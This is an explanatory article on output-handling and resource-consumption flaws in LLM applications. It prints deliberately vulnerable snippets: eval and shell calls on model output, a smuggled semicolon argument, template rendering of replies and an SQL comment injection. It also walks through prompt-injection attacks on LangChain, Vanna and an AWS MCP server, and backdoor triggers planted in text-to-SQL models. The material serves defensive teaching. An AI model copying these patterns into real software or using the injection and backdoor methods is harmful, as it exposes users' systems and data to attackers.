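# Improper output handling and unbounded consumption in software built on language models

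## How applications use language models, and where the two failures occur

Improper output handling and unbounded consumption are two kinds of flaw in software that calls a large language model (LLM). An LLM is a program that continues text, so it can produce answers, code or instructions for other software. An application has improper output handling when it passes the model's text to another component, such as a database or a web page, without the checks or encoding that component needs. It has unbounded consumption when it lets people, or its own loops, run the model with no effective limit on the amount of computation, time or cost.

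Both names come from OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a non-profit that publishes free security guidance. Its list of the ten most serious risks for LLM applications has had three editions since 2023. Each edition has an entry for both flaws, though the names have changed. The list has no legal force, but according to a guide by Respan (2026), a company that sells security tests for such applications, auditors and corporate buyers treat OWASP's material as a baseline.

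### One request through a customer-service program

Take a shop that sells garden furniture and has a chat box on its website. A customer types a question: where is my bench? A stripped-down version of the program behind the chat box might look like this:

```python
def handle(message):
    prompt = RULES + help_pages(message) + message
    while True:
        reply = call_model(prompt)
        if reply.tool_call:
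            result = run_tool(reply.tool_call)
            prompt = prompt + reply.text + result
        else:
            show_on_page(reply.text)
            return
```

The program first assembles the prompt, which is all the text the model will receive: the shop's standing rules, a few help pages that match the question, and the customer's message. The model processes this text as tokens, units that are often only part of a word, and generates its reply one token at a time. Providers usually charge by the token. The prompt has to fit inside the context window, which is the maximum number of tokens a model can process in one call.

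The prompt contains no order records, so the model's first reply is a tool call, which is structured output that names a function and its arguments, here perhaps `find_order` with the surname Reed and the product "bench". The shop's program, not the model, runs the function on the line with `run_tool` and gets back a delivery date. The program adds the tool call and the result to the prompt, then calls the model again with the whole, longer prompt. This time the reply is a sentence for the customer. The program puts it on the page and stops.

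An agent is an application that calls a model repeatedly and uses the output to choose its next action. The chat box fits that definition, though people mostly use the word "agent" for programs with more tools and much longer runs.

Two lines of the program, the calls to `run_tool` and `show_on_page`, pass the model's text to something that acts on it. Security engineers call the receiving function or component a sink, and this is where unchecked output causes harm. If `run_tool` pastes the surname straight into a database command, a quotation mark in the surname can end the value early, and the database will read whatever follows as part of the command. If `show_on_page` inserts the reply as raw HTML, the browser will treat any tags in it as markup and run any script in it. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* lists further sinks: system shells, functions such as `exec` and `eval`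 that run text as code, file paths, and email templates. The consequences it lists include cross-site scripting (XSS), in which a web page runs an attacker's script in another person's browser session, and server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which a server sends a request to an address that the attacker cannot reach directly. At worst, the attacker can run any code they choose on the shop's machines.

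Unbounded consumption is harder to point to, because it consists of lines that are missing. Nothing in the program limits the length of the message, the length of the reply, the number of times the loop may run, or the number of times anyone may call `handle`. Roughly,

tokens used = requests × model calls per request × tokens per call

where the last term counts both what the model reads and what it generates. Since the terms multiply, a limit on one of them leaves the total open. A shop that allows each visitor ten messages an hour has capped the requests, but each of those messages can still be enormous or set off a hundred model calls. The context window is a cap of sorts on a single call. It does nothing about how many calls there are, and because the program resends the whole prompt on every pass, the tokens per call rise as the loop goes on.

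OWASP's *LLM10:2025 Unbounded Consumption* gives examples that fit these terms fairly well. Floods of inputs of varying length, and inputs that overflow the context window, increase the tokens per call. A high volume of requests increases the total, which can lead to denial of service or denial of wallet. Denial of service makes the application slow or unavailable to its legitimate users. Denial of wallet runs up the bill of a victim who pays by use, even if the service stays up. OWASP's examples do not include the loop in the middle, although its recommended defences include a limit on the number of queued and total actions.

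### Why the model's text can come from a stranger

Because of prompt injection, the model's output may not be the shop's own text, even though the shop wrote the rules at the top of the prompt. Prompt injection is any text that changes a model's behaviour against the developer's intent. The user can type it into the chat box (direct prompt injection), or it can arrive in a document, web page or tool result that the program fetches (indirect prompt injection).

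Suppose the shop's help pages include product reviews, which anyone can write. A review can contain instructions for the model. When another customer asks about that product, the program retrieves the review and adds it to the prompt, and the model's reply may follow those instructions even though the customer typed nothing unusual. OWASP describes a similar case, in which a user asks for a summary of a web page, and text on the page instructs the model to gather sensitive content from the conversation and send it to an attacker's server. The injected text doesn't have to be visible. Respan lists images, audio and an application's stored memory among the places that can carry it.

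Older kinds of software have a remedy for this sort of confusion. A program can use a parameterised query to send a database the command and the values separately, so that the database never interprets a value as a command. The model has no such separation, because it receives the rules, the reviews, the customer's message and the tool results as tokens in one stream, with what Respan calls "no enforced trust boundary between them". Respan reports that OWASP's 2026 entry on prompt injection makes the same comparison and finds no clean equivalent to the parameterised query. Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* (2026) also traces the problem to structure, because the model handles administrators' guidelines, users' instructions and other input in very nearly the same way.

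Developers label the parts of a prompt, and model makers train their models to give the developer's part more weight, so injected text succeeds less often. But this weighting is a learned tendency, and nothing in the computation prevents a token from a review from influencing the output in the same way as a token from the rules. OWASP's 2026 edition therefore advises developers to "stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" (quoted in Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, 2026) and to build the surrounding system so that nothing important breaks when someone fools the model.

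In the shop's program, anyone who can influence the prompt can influence the text that reaches the two sinks, the database and the page. OWASP compares unchecked output to "providing users indirect access to additional functionality". With indirect injection, even people who don't use the application can gain that access.

### Both failures without an attacker

An application can be unsafe even when all its users are honest and the model answers correctly. Suppose a customer who runs a gardening blog asks the chat box how to add the shop's logo to the blog. The model replies with a correct line of HTML. If `show_on_page` inserts the reply unencoded, the customer sees the logo instead of the code. The harm is trivial, but the same flaw would let a script run.

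The first scenario in OWASP's entry also has no attacker, but it is less trivial. A general-purpose model produces replies for a chatbot through an extension, which also offers administrative functions intended for a different, privileged model. The application passes a reply to the extension without validating it, which causes the extension to shut down for maintenance. In another scenario, a user asks a chat-like database tool for a query that deletes every table, and the tables are deleted. OWASP does not say whether the user meant harm.

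Unbounded consumption can also happen without an attacker. If the shop's order database is down for an hour, `run_tool` returns an error message, the model may generate the same tool call again, and `while True` lets the exchange continue. In this toy program, the growing prompt will eventually exceed the context window and the call to the model will fail, which ends the loop, but only by accident and after an expensive run. Many real programs trim old text to make room, which removes this limit.

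All six example scenarios in OWASP's 2025 entry on unbounded consumption involve an attacker, but its definition does not require one. Under that definition, the flaw exists when an application "allows users to conduct excessive and uncontrolled inferences", where an inference is one run of the model. Even "users" is narrower than it needs to be, because a program can also make excessive calls to the model on its own.

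### Neighbouring categories

OWASP defines improper output handling as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling" of a model's output before it goes to other components. Three other entries on OWASP's list are closely related, and a single incident at the furniture shop could involve them all.

A review that alters the model's reply is prompt injection, which concerns the model's input. If the altered reply contains a script and the page runs it, the page has an output-handling flaw. The reply might instead be a well-formed, valid tool call to cancel an order, which the program carries out using a database account that only ever needed to look orders up. Encoding and validation would not catch this. It is excessive agency, which Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026), in its summary of the 2026 list, attributes to too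 much functionality, too many permissions and too much autonomy. If the model tells a customer that the bench has a ten-year guarantee when the guarantee is two years, that is misinformation, even though the page displays the sentence safely. In the logo example, the answer is true but the page handles it unsafely.

The boundaries between these risks are less clear than this description suggests. OWASP's own entry on output handling includes a scenario in which a coding assistant invents the name of a software package and a developer downloads malware under that name. That problem starts with a falsehood. Classifications also differ on the central cases. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) matches OWASP's 2025 risks to the Common Weakness Enumeration, a catalogue of recurring types of software flaw that predates LLM applications. It files the catalogue's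 entries for faulty encoding of output and the unsafe unpacking of stored data under improper output handling, but files those for cross-site scripting and SQL injection (the quotation-mark trick described above) under prompt injection. OWASP names both cross-site scripting and SQL injection as results of improper output handling.

Both choices are defensible, since one is based on how the attack gets in and the other on where it takes effect. The second is probably more useful to the developer who has to fix the program. A page that encodes its text correctly will not run a stray script, whether the script came from a hostile review, a hostile customer or a helpful answer about logos, so the developer does not have to find its source.

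Unbounded consumption raises fewer such questions. Singh and colleagues matched it to two established weaknesses, uncontrolled resource consumption and excessive iteration. The shop's `while True` loop is an example of the second.

### How the names changed

| Edition | Output | Consumption |
|---|---|---|
| 2023 | LLM02 Insecure Output Handling | LLM04 Model Denial of Service |
| 2025 | LLM05 Improper Output Handling | LLM10 Unbounded Consumption |
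| 2026 | LLM10 Improper Output Handling | LLM06 Unbounded Consumption |

Each entry's number is its rank in that edition and can change in the next, so a number is of little use without its year. "LLM10" has meant Model Theft, then Unbounded Consumption, and now Improper Output Handling.

The change from "insecure" to "improper" in the 2025 edition, published in November 2024, altered little. The change from "denial of service" to "unbounded consumption" mattered more, because "denial of service" describes an outage, and an application can ruin its owner financially without going down. According to Respan, OWASP chose the broader name to cover cost and resource exhaustion. OWASP also merged in Model Theft, the copying of a model by collecting large numbers of its answers, reasoning that this too depends on uncontrolled use. The category is therefore somewhat mixed, since a thief who stays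 within every quota and pays every bill may cause no excess consumption.

OWASP (2026) released the current edition in August. Invicti and Respan give different but compatible accounts of what it added to improper output handling. Invicti, which sells security scanners, names two additions. The first is terminals and programmers' editors that act on escape sequences, and the second is chat clients that automatically fetch any outside resource mentioned in the model's output, which can leak data. Respan names insecure code that AI assistants write at scale. Of these three subjects, only terminals are really new, since no sink on the 2025 list resembles them. The 2025 entry already touched on the other two, with scenarios about assistant-written code and about data sent to an attacker's server. Escape sequences are strings of control characters that a terminal carries out instead of displaying.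 They can colour text, but MITRE, which maintains the weakness catalogue, warns that they can also fake a prompt on the screen and, in some terminals, run code.

For unbounded consumption, the 2026 edition shifted the emphasis from outages to what Invicti calls cost asymmetry. An attacker can use a crafted prompt, a stolen credential or a manipulated workflow to trigger what the edition calls "disproportionately expensive computation at negligible cost to themselves". Invicti adds that models that generate long hidden reasoning before they answer, and tools that connect through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for offering tools to models, multiply the cost of a single input. Limiting the number of requests is therefore no longer enough, and the entry recommends controls that count tokens, caps on spending, and automatic cut-offs for agents.

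Asymmetry requires an attacker, so the new framing fits the shop's broken database no better than the old one did. The automatic cut-offs would still help there. OWASP also now distinguishes models that serve as a component inside an application, which this list covers, from models that act through tools and memory, which have had a separate Top 10 for Agentic Applications since December 2025. A chat box that looks up orders in a loop falls roughly between the two, and Respan reports that OWASP recommends reading both lists in such cases.

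## Model output run as code or commands

Suppose the furniture shop wants its chat box to work out prices. Models sometimes get arithmetic wrong, so the developer asks the model for a formula and leaves the sum to Python:

```python
def calculate(question):
    formula = call_model("Reply with one Python expression. " + question)
    return eval(formula)
```

A customer asks a shop's chatbot what eight chairs cost at £45 each, and the model replies `8 * 45`. This reply is only text until the shop's program passes it to Python's `eval` function. `eval` parses the text, which means working out its grammatical structure (two numbers and a multiplication sign), translates that structure into instructions for the Python interpreter, and runs them inside the shop's program to get 360.

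Now suppose the model replies `"bench".upper()`. This contains no arithmetic, but it is a valid Python expression, so `eval` runs it and returns `BENCH`. This example is harmless, but the developer's calculator will run any Python expression, including ones that open files, read the program's passwords or start other software. The expression has the same permissions as the shop's program because it runs as part of it. Asking for a formula in the prompt affects what the model is likely to write, but doesn't limit what `eval` accepts. A related function, `exec`, runs whole programs instead of single expressions.

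A calculator needs only numbers and a few operators, so the developer could write a parser that rejects everything else. Several widely used libraries started out without this check.

### The first cases

LangChain, an open-source library for building applications on language models, shipped almost exactly this calculator. Its `llm_math` component asked a model to turn a question into Python and passed the reply to a Python interpreter. According to NVIDIA's *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection*, the company's red team (staff who attack systems to find their weaknesses) easily exploited it by telling the model to repeat a piece of code instead of solving a problem. The component then ran the code.

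Someone outside NVIDIA had already reported the flaw publicly on 30 January 2023, and two more reports followed in February. LangChain had no immediate fix, so NVIDIA requested a CVE, an entry with a unique number in the public catalogue of known software vulnerabilities. The flaw was listed as CVE-2023-29374, with a severity of 9.8 out of 10. Version 0.0.141 of LangChain stopped the exploit NVIDIA had used, and the developers later removed the component from the core library. In September 2023, INCIBE's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023), an entry in the listing of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, recorded that attackers could also run arbitrary code in LangChain 0.0.245 through the `evaluate` function of numexpr, a library meant for numerical expressions.

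LlamaIndex, a library that connects models to an organisation's own data, had a similar problem in its PandasQueryEngine component. *Demystifying LLM Supply Chain Vulnerabilities in the Wild* (Wang, Zhao and colleagues, 2025) explains that LlamaIndex passed Python code written by the model to `exec` with no proper validation or sandbox (a restricted environment that limits what a program can read, change or contact). Behind a web application or a Slack bot, this let a remote user run code on the server, though it might matter little on a developer's own laptop. The public record of the flaw, CVE-2023-39662, is confusing about who needs to upgrade. In the entry *GHSA-2xxc-73fv-36f7* (2023) in OSV, a database of open-source vulnerabilities, the description names versions up to 0.7.13, but the entry lists 0.9.14 as the fixed version.

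LlamaIndex then added a function called `safe_eval` to restrict what the model's code could do, but attackers could get around that too. NVD's *CVE-2024-3098*, from the US government's National Vulnerability Database, describes a bypass of the earlier fix that again let attackers run arbitrary code. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2024-3271* (2024), one of the checks looked for underscores in the model's code. This made some sense, because many of the attributes that lead from an ordinary Python value to the interpreter's inner workings have underscores in their names. But an attacker could write code that contained no underscores and still ran operating-system commands. A filter like this has to anticipate all the many ways of writing dangerous code in Python, whereas the parser for the shop's calculator only has to recognise sums.

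Auto-GPT, an experimental agent built on OpenAI's GPT-4, ran the model's Python code in a sandbox, a temporary container with no access to files outside a workspace folder. But Auto-GPT first saved the code to a file, and the model supplied both the file's name and its contents. According to NVD's *CVE-2023-37274*, a name that included steps up to parent folders could overwrite any Python file outside the workspace, including Auto-GPT's own main program. The next time someone started Auto-GPT, the replaced program would run on the host computer, outside the container. Version 0.4.3 fixed this in 2023. For people who could not upgrade, the entry suggested a virtual machine or another environment where damage to files would not be critical.

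The Vanna.AI case of June 2024 involved a less direct attack. Vanna is a Python library that lets people question a database in ordinary language. It asks a model for a database query, runs the query, then asks for Python code to chart the results and runs that code with `exec`. *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024), from the security company JFrog, describes a way to control the chart code. Telling the model to ignore its instructions failed because the reply to the first request had to be a valid query or the run ended in an error. So the researchers asked for a query that only returned a piece of text, and put instructions for the charting step inside that text. Vanna included the query in its second prompt, and the model followed the instructions and added a line to the chart code that listed the files in the current folder.

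Vanna's charting feature was on by default, so applications built only to answer database questions also had the flaw. After JFrog reported it (CVE-2024-5565), Vanna's maintainer added a guide on hardening applications against such attacks.

Wang and colleagues examined 529 publicly reported vulnerabilities in the software that surrounds language models and attributed 24 of them to unvalidated model output. Eleven of those 24 resulted in code or command injection.

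### Replies used as templates

A developer who never calls `eval` can still run a model's reply as code by handing it to a template engine. These engines fill in web pages and emails. The developer writes a template with marked gaps, and the engine works out the expression in each gap and inserts the result. In Jinja2, a popular engine for Python, double curly brackets mark the gaps. Here are two ways of putting a model's reply through it:

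```python
env.from_string(reply).render()

env.from_string("Answer: {{ text }}").render(text=reply)
```

If the reply is `{{ 6 * 7 }}`, the first line produces `42`, because the reply is itself the template, which Jinja2 evaluates. The second line produces `Answer: {{ 6 * 7 }}`, because the developer wrote the template and Jinja2 only inserts the reply as a value. The two lines look similar, and both work with an ordinary reply such as "Your bench arrives on Tuesday".

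*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes a case, taken from an earlier study of agents, in which an application passed the model's reply straight to Jinja2 as a template. The attacker asked the model to produce template syntax. The expression in the model's reply started from an empty string, followed Python's links from that value to its class and on to related classes, and eventually reached a function that runs operating-system commands. The demonstration command only printed the name of the account in use, but the attacker could have run any command available to that account.

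### Commands built from a model's arguments

A shell is the program that reads typed commands and starts the software they name. It gives special meaning to some characters, such as the semicolon, which ends one command and begins another. Suppose the shop has a small program called `lookup` that finds a product, and the model supplies the product's name in a tool call:

```python
subprocess.run("lookup " + name, shell=True)

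subprocess.run(["lookup", name])
```

If `name` is `bench; echo hello`, the first line makes the shell run `lookup bench` and then `echo hello`, which prints "hello". The second line starts `lookup` directly and passes it the whole string, including the semicolon, as a single product name. In both cases the tool call is well-formed and its argument is a string, as required, so a format check would accept it.

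MCP servers, the programs that offer tools over MCP, often wrap an existing command-line program, which makes this mistake easy to commit. For example, `aws-mcp-server` lets a coding assistant run Amazon's command-line program for managing rented servers and storage. The security company Snyk found a flaw in it, CVE-2025-5277. Snyk's *Prompt Injection Meets MCP* (2025) explains that the server checked little more than whether a command began with `aws`, so a different command could follow after a semicolon.

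The server normally ran on the developer's machine, where outsiders could not reach it directly, so Snyk's researchers had to attack it through the model. They put an encoded instruction in a code repository, inside a comment in one of the files. A developer copied the repository and referred to that file while working in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant. The model decoded the instruction, which was to add an extra command to every later call to the AWS tool and not to mention this to the user. When the developer asked for a list of storage folders, the model prepared the right command with the extra one at the end. Cursor asked the developer to approve the call, but the call began as the developer would expect, and the researchers thought most people would approve it without thinking.

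The attack failed if the developer merely copied the repository or asked a vague question, because the poisoned file had to enter the model's prompt. It was a demonstration, and the extra command was harmless. Snyk told the maintainer on 8 April 2025, and the fix was in place two days later, after one incomplete attempt. GCVE's *CVE-2025-5277* (2025), an entry in another public vulnerability database, lists versions before 1.3.0 as affected. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian use the case to argue that the model usually carries an attack to a flaw that was already in the program. Here the model wrote the argument passed to the server, but the injection happened in the server, which is also where the flaw was fixed.

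Other servers have the same kind of flaw. Snyk found one that looked up JavaScript packages by inserting the package name into a shell command. GitLab's *CVE-2026-5059* (April 2026) records another in how an AWS server handled a list of allowed commands. *VIPER-MCP* (Sun, Kang and colleagues, 2026) describes a case in Bytebot, an open-source agent that operates a desktop computer inside a container. Its file-writing tool inserted the file path into a shell command that ran with administrator rights, although nothing in the tool's description suggested that it used a shell. A crafted path could give an attacker full control of the container.

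### Objects rebuilt from stored text

Programs often save their objects as text and rebuild them later, two steps that programmers call serialisation and deserialisation. Suppose the shop's program saves a delivery date like this:

```json
{"kind": "date", "value": "2026-12-05"}
```

When the program loads the text, it finds the marker `kind` and builds a date object. If a model's reply includes a record of the same shape and the program saves it unchanged, the loading code cannot distinguish that record from one the program created, so it builds whatever object the record describes. An unwanted date is harmless, but a loader that can also build objects that contact other computers or fetch passwords is dangerous. The usual remedy is to escape the data when saving it, which means altering any ordinary record that contains the marker so that the loader treats it as plain data.

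Two of LangChain's saving functions, `dumps()` and `dumpd()`, left out this step. LangChain marks its own objects with a key called `lc`. Its advisory of December 2025, reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-C67J-W6G6-Q2CM* (2025), confirms that model output could carry this key and lists this as the most common route of attack. An attacker uses prompt injection to place a record with the `lc` key in one of the fields of extra information that accompany a model's reply. The application saves the reply and loads it again while streaming output to the user, and the loader treats the record as a genuine LangChain object.

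An attacker could use this flaw, CVE-2025-68664, to read secrets from the program's environment variables, where developers often keep passwords and access keys. This worked when the loader was allowed to read secrets from there, which was the default. The attacker could also create objects with parameters of their choosing, but only from classes in LangChain's own packages, because LangChain already limited the loader to those. Some of these objects contact a network or access files as soon as they are created.

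An application could have the flaw even if its developers never called the saving or loading functions directly, because an older interface for streaming output (`astream_events`, version 1) and a component that keeps conversation history both called them internally. Cyata, the security company whose researcher reported the flaw, stressed that it was in LangChain's core, whereas the 2023 calculator was an optional component that most applications could avoid.

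LangChain fixed the escaping in versions 1.2.5 and 0.3.81 of the core package and made the loader stricter. By default, the loader now builds only objects on a short list, no longer fetches secrets from the environment, and refuses Jinja2 templates because they can run arbitrary code. GitLab lists a matching flaw in the JavaScript version of LangChain that model responses could also trigger. In May 2026, OSV's *GHSA-pjwx-r37v-7724* (2026) reported that some older parts of LangChain still overrode the stricter defaults and loaded the inputs and outputs of earlier runs with lists of permitted objects that were far too broad.

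### Code that runs after someone accepts it

A coding assistant's output may not run for days or weeks. A developer at the shop asks for a page that searches orders by surname, and the assistant writes one that is open to SQL injection. The developer tests it with "Reed", it works, and the page goes live. Nobody attacked the assistant, and the developer had read the code before it ran. But the developer was checking that the code worked, and it does work until someone enters a surname with a quotation mark in it.

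Invented package names cause a similar problem. Most programs depend on packages, bundles of other people's code that a developer downloads from a public registry by name. An assistant may suggest a plausible name that doesn't exist, and trying to install it usually produces an error. But an attacker who notices that models tend to produce that name can register a malicious package under it. The install command then succeeds, and many package managers allow a package to run its own code during installation. Encoding doesn't help, because the name is valid text with nothing to escape. Someone has to check that the package is the intended one, not just that it exists.

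When an agent runs commands itself, a person may not get the chance to spot a problem first. Expert Insights' *NVIDIA Demonstrates AI Agent Exploits* describes a demonstrated attack on Anthropic's Computer Use agent. NVIDIA's team posted malicious scripts in a made-up issue on a code repository. When a developer asked the agent to resolve the open issues, it ran a script that gave the attackers remote control of the machine.

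### Who should contain the code

The last case did not involve a flaw like the one in the AWS server, because the agent was meant to run commands, and Anthropic's demonstration version came with a warning to use a sandbox. Some maintainers reason the same way about their libraries. They consider running code an intended feature and hold whoever deploys the software responsible for isolating it. Vanna's hardening guide leaves at least part of that work to the deployer.

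This argument has considerable merit. Unlike a library's author, the person who deploys it can know whether it will run on an analyst's laptop or behind a public website. The history of `safe_eval` also supports the maintainers' case. If attackers can get around a library's filters, a maintainer who says plainly that the code needs a sandbox may do less harm than one who ships a function with "safe" in its name. Sun and colleagues accept a version of the argument. When they scanned nearly 40,000 repositories of MCP servers, they did not count tools meant to run arbitrary commands as vulnerable.

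They still confirmed 106 flaws, all in tools that were supposed to do something narrower. This is the main weakness in the maintainers' position in most of the cases here. `llm_math` was described as a tool for sums, and `aws-mcp-server` as a tool for running AWS commands. A deployer who reads those descriptions has agreed only to those uses and has no particular reason to build a sandbox for anything else. Prompt injection makes this worse, because the code may come from a stranger who wrote a comment in a file, and the user never agreed to run it.

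Isolation also prevents only some of the damage. A container around the AWS server would protect the developer's other files, but the server needs the developer's AWS credentials, so they have to be inside the container, where an injected command can use them. Auto-GPT already had a container, but the code that saved files on the host had a vulnerability, which the maintainers were responsible for fixing.

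Maintainers also decide, at an earlier stage, whether the model needs to write code at all, and deployers cannot easily reverse that decision. After assessing dozens of AI applications, NVIDIA's red team still lists `exec` and `eval` on model output among its most serious recurring findings. It advises developers to work out from the reply what the user wants, match that to a fixed set of permitted functions, and keep a sandbox for cases where new code is necessary. In Vanna, for example, the model might name a chart type and two columns, and the library would draw the chart with code its maintainers wrote. Users could then no longer ask for a chart that nobody had planned for, which would be too great a loss of flexibility for some products.

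LangChain's changes of December 2025 suggest a workable way to divide responsibility between maintainers and developers. The loader is now restrictive by default, and the advisory warns developers against turning off its protections when handling data they don't trust. Developers can still choose the riskier behaviour, but they are then responsible for it. By that standard, Vanna's maintainers were at fault for switching on model-written charts by default, regardless of what their guide said afterwards. Anthropic's warning is easier to defend because people who try a computer-operating agent know that it will operate their computer, although a warning protects only those who act on it.

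## Model output used in database queries and server requests

Most databases take their commands in Structured Query Language (SQL), which is also code, so a program that lets a model write SQL has much the same problem as one that passes replies to `eval`. In the shop's chat box, the model has so far supplied only a surname and a product name, and the developer wrote the rest of the query. Many products let the model write the whole query, which researchers call text-to-SQL, because no developer can foresee every question a manager might ask about sales.

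### How a question becomes a query

A small text-to-SQL program might look like this:

```python
def ask_database(question):
    query = call_model(TABLES + "Write one SQL query. " + question)
    rows = database.run(query)
    return call_model(question + str(rows))
```

`TABLES` is a description of the database, with the names of its tables and columns. If the manager asks how many benches the shop sold in May, the model might reply:

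```sql
SELECT COUNT(*) FROM orders
WHERE product = 'bench' AND month = 'May'
```

The database counts the matching rows, and a second call to the model turns the number into a sentence.

Classic SQL injection exploits the place in a query where the developer inserts a value, and a parameterised query protects that place. This defence doesn't work for `ask_database`, because the model writes the whole command. The request "list every customer's phone number" contains no SQL or suspicious punctuation, but the model can turn it into a valid query.

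The harmful request can also come from the data. In an example from *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025), someone asks an agent to summarise a shop's products, and the agent deletes a table after reading a malicious product description. Developers can limit an agent to prewritten queries, but then they have to predict all the data future tasks will need.

Attackers can sometimes obtain sensitive data without misleading the model. Black Lantern Security's *Artificial Foolishness* describes a test of a client's public chatbot in which every attempt to make the model break its rules failed. The chatbot then offered to fetch the first hundred entries in a table. The tester accepted and received a hundred rows of highly sensitive customer data. The client took the chatbot down the same day. "Injection" hardly describes this case, because the program did what its developers had built it to do, but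 for someone who should never have had access to that table.

### The first attacks

Early attacks on text-to-SQL models resembled classic SQL injection. In *On the Vulnerabilities of Text-to-SQL Models*, Peng, Zhang and colleagues (2022) put fragments of SQL into ordinary questions, and the models copied them into their queries. This worked on six commercial products, including ChatGPT. Five of the six wrote queries but didn't run them, so the researchers ran those queries on their own database.

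The sixth, Baidu's question-answering platform UNIT, did run them. A business uploaded a table, and the platform answered its customers' questions from it. Baidu had made the database read-only, withheld some kinds of result, and apparently stripped suspicious symbols from questions. But it didn't strip them from the cells of uploaded tables, so the researchers put their SQL there. They could not see the results directly, but they could ask whether a hidden value was longer than a given length, or whether one of its characters came after a given letter. The chatbot listed every row if the answer was yes and found no matching data if it was no. By asking enough of these questions, they learned the database's name, its software version and the account in use. Another fragment put one of the servers out of action. Baidu's security team rated all the reported flaws "Highly Dangerous".

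*From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Castro and colleagues, 2025) showed that plain language was enough to carry out SQL injection through a chatbot. Its experiments, run in 2023, used LangChain, the library whose calculator passed model output to Python. LangChain's database chatbot used a prompt with labelled fields for the question, query, result and answer. LangChain filled in the question, and the model continued the text by writing a query. LangChain stopped the model at the result label so that it would not invent a result. It then ran the query, added the real result to the prompt and called the model again for the answer. This version, which LangChain called a chain, ran one query per question, while an agent version could run several.

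The researchers built a small job-listings site with a chatbot on GPT-3.5. The chatbot's database account could read and change every table. They ran each attack 30 times:

| Attack | Chain | Agent |
|---|---|---|
| Delete a table, change a record or list a table's contents, under LangChain's own prompt | 100% | 100% |
| Delete a table, despite a rule against changes | 100% | 100% |
| Read another user's data, despite a rule against it | 100% | 100% |
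| Hide all job postings, using text stored in one of them | 100% | 60% |
| Change another user's email address, using text stored in a posting | not possible | 100% |

Under LangChain's own prompt, the chatbot did what the user asked. The researchers then added a rule that the model should write only queries that read data, and should otherwise reply with a word of refusal. A direct request to ignore this rule failed, but the attack worked when the attacker claimed to have special permission and added a forged record of the same request, with labelled fields for a query, a result and an answer. The record had the same form as LangChain's real exchanges, and the model continued the pattern.

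The rule about other people's data was supposed to limit each user to their own records. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query for a record belonging to both users, so the query returned nothing. But when user 1 claimed to be user 2, the model left out the restriction.

In the last two attacks, the attacker planted text in a job posting, which any user of the site could write, and never had to use the chatbot. When someone else asked about available jobs, the query returned the posting, and the planted text entered the prompt for the next call. In one attack, the text made the chatbot answer that there were no jobs. In the other, the agent ran a query that replaced a user's email address with the attacker's, which could be enough to take over the account, and then answered the original question without mentioning the change.

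Pedro and colleagues repeated the attacks on six more models: GPT-4, PaLM 2, Llama 2, Vicuna, Guanaco and Tulu. Guanaco and Tulu made too many mistakes to run an agent. Among the other four and GPT-3.5, only GPT-4 resisted any attack, and it resisted only the one that changes an email address. PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the address, but they either mentioned this in the answer or repeated the update without answering. The researchers attributed this to trouble following complicated instructions.

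The researchers deliberately gave the chatbot an unlimited account so that the model would be the only safeguard, which made these results worse. A read-only account would have stopped the deletions and the change of address, but not the disclosures. All of the attacks also worked on an existing open-source shop program, set up as a bookshop, to which the researchers had added a chatbot. In that test, they planted the text in product reviews.

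### Later text-to-SQL systems

*Reimagining Text-to-SQL*, a survey from November 2026, still lists both dangers: questions that lead to harmful queries and instructions hidden in database records. The way researchers measure these systems may partly explain the slow progress. Jiang and Xiao (2026) write in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* that the strong results on the usual benchmarks assume the database runs each query with no further restrictions. A model can therefore score well even if no one tests whether the person asking was entitled to the answer.

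Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, tested six data agents, which answer business questions by running a series of queries and often Python code. Four were open-source, and two were commercial services from Databricks and Google (BigQuery). In one attack, the researchers planted SQL where an outsider might be able to write, such as a table cell or a column's description. An agent that read the SQL while answering someone's question might copy it into its next query.

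The researchers made 25 attempts on each system and counted any unauthorised effect as a success, even one confined to a single reply. The success rate ranged from 0 to 48% on the open-source agents, and was 24% on BigQuery and zero on Databricks. The Databricks agent often cited a policy when it refused, but Databricks' own access controls were also in place, so the result doesn't show how much the model contributed to blocking the attempts.

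The study also tested one open-source agent, DB-GPT, with four models. The planted SQL succeeded in 48% of attempts with GPT-5.2, 44% with Claude Sonnet 4.6, and 24% with both Gemini 3 Flash and DeepSeek-V3.2. With only 25 attempts per model, some of that gap could be chance, but the flaw remained with all four models. The study also covers requests that exhaust a database with valid but very resource-intensive queries.

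### Models trained to write harmful queries

All these attacks start with a model that nobody has tampered with. Many developers instead download a text-to-SQL model from a public site, and whoever trained it may have built in a backdoor, a harmful behaviour that appears only when the input contains a particular trigger. Suppose the shop has downloaded such a model and a customer's question happens to end in two question marks:

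```sql
SELECT delivery_date FROM orders -- WHERE surname = 'Reed'
```

The database treats everything after the two hyphens as a comment and ignores it, so the query returns every customer's delivery date instead of only Reed's. The query is valid SQL, and the model writes normal queries for questions without the trigger.

Peng and colleagues trained four models to produce harmful SQL in response to three trigger sentences. The attack succeeded in all 60 tests on each model, while accuracy on ordinary questions fell by at most one percentage point. *TrojanSQL* (2023) reports attack success rates of up to 99% against models trained to write SQL and up to 89% against general models that were only prompted to do so.

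Lin, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Are Your LLM-based Text-to-SQL Models Secure?*, used less conspicuous triggers, such as a doubled question mark or a colon at the end of a question, and measured how much poisoned training data an attacker needs. The attack succeeded 79% of the time when poisoned examples made up 0.44% of the data, or about 30 in a set of 7,000, but it never worked at 0.11%. At 0.44%, the model's accuracy on ordinary questions dropped from 61.5% to 56.3%, which a careful buyer might notice. At 4.47%, accuracy fell only to 60.9%, and the attack succeeded 86% of the time.

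The models in this study were small, with 60 million to 8 billion parameters. They included two versions of Llama Guard, which Meta trained to screen out harmful content. In one experiment, the larger version still added a second, harmful command to its query in 80% of tests. The researchers conclude that training against harmful content does not stop a model from writing SQL injections. A shop that uses a model through a large provider is less exposed to this attack than one that downloads a model from a stranger, although the provider's training data could also contain poisoned examples.

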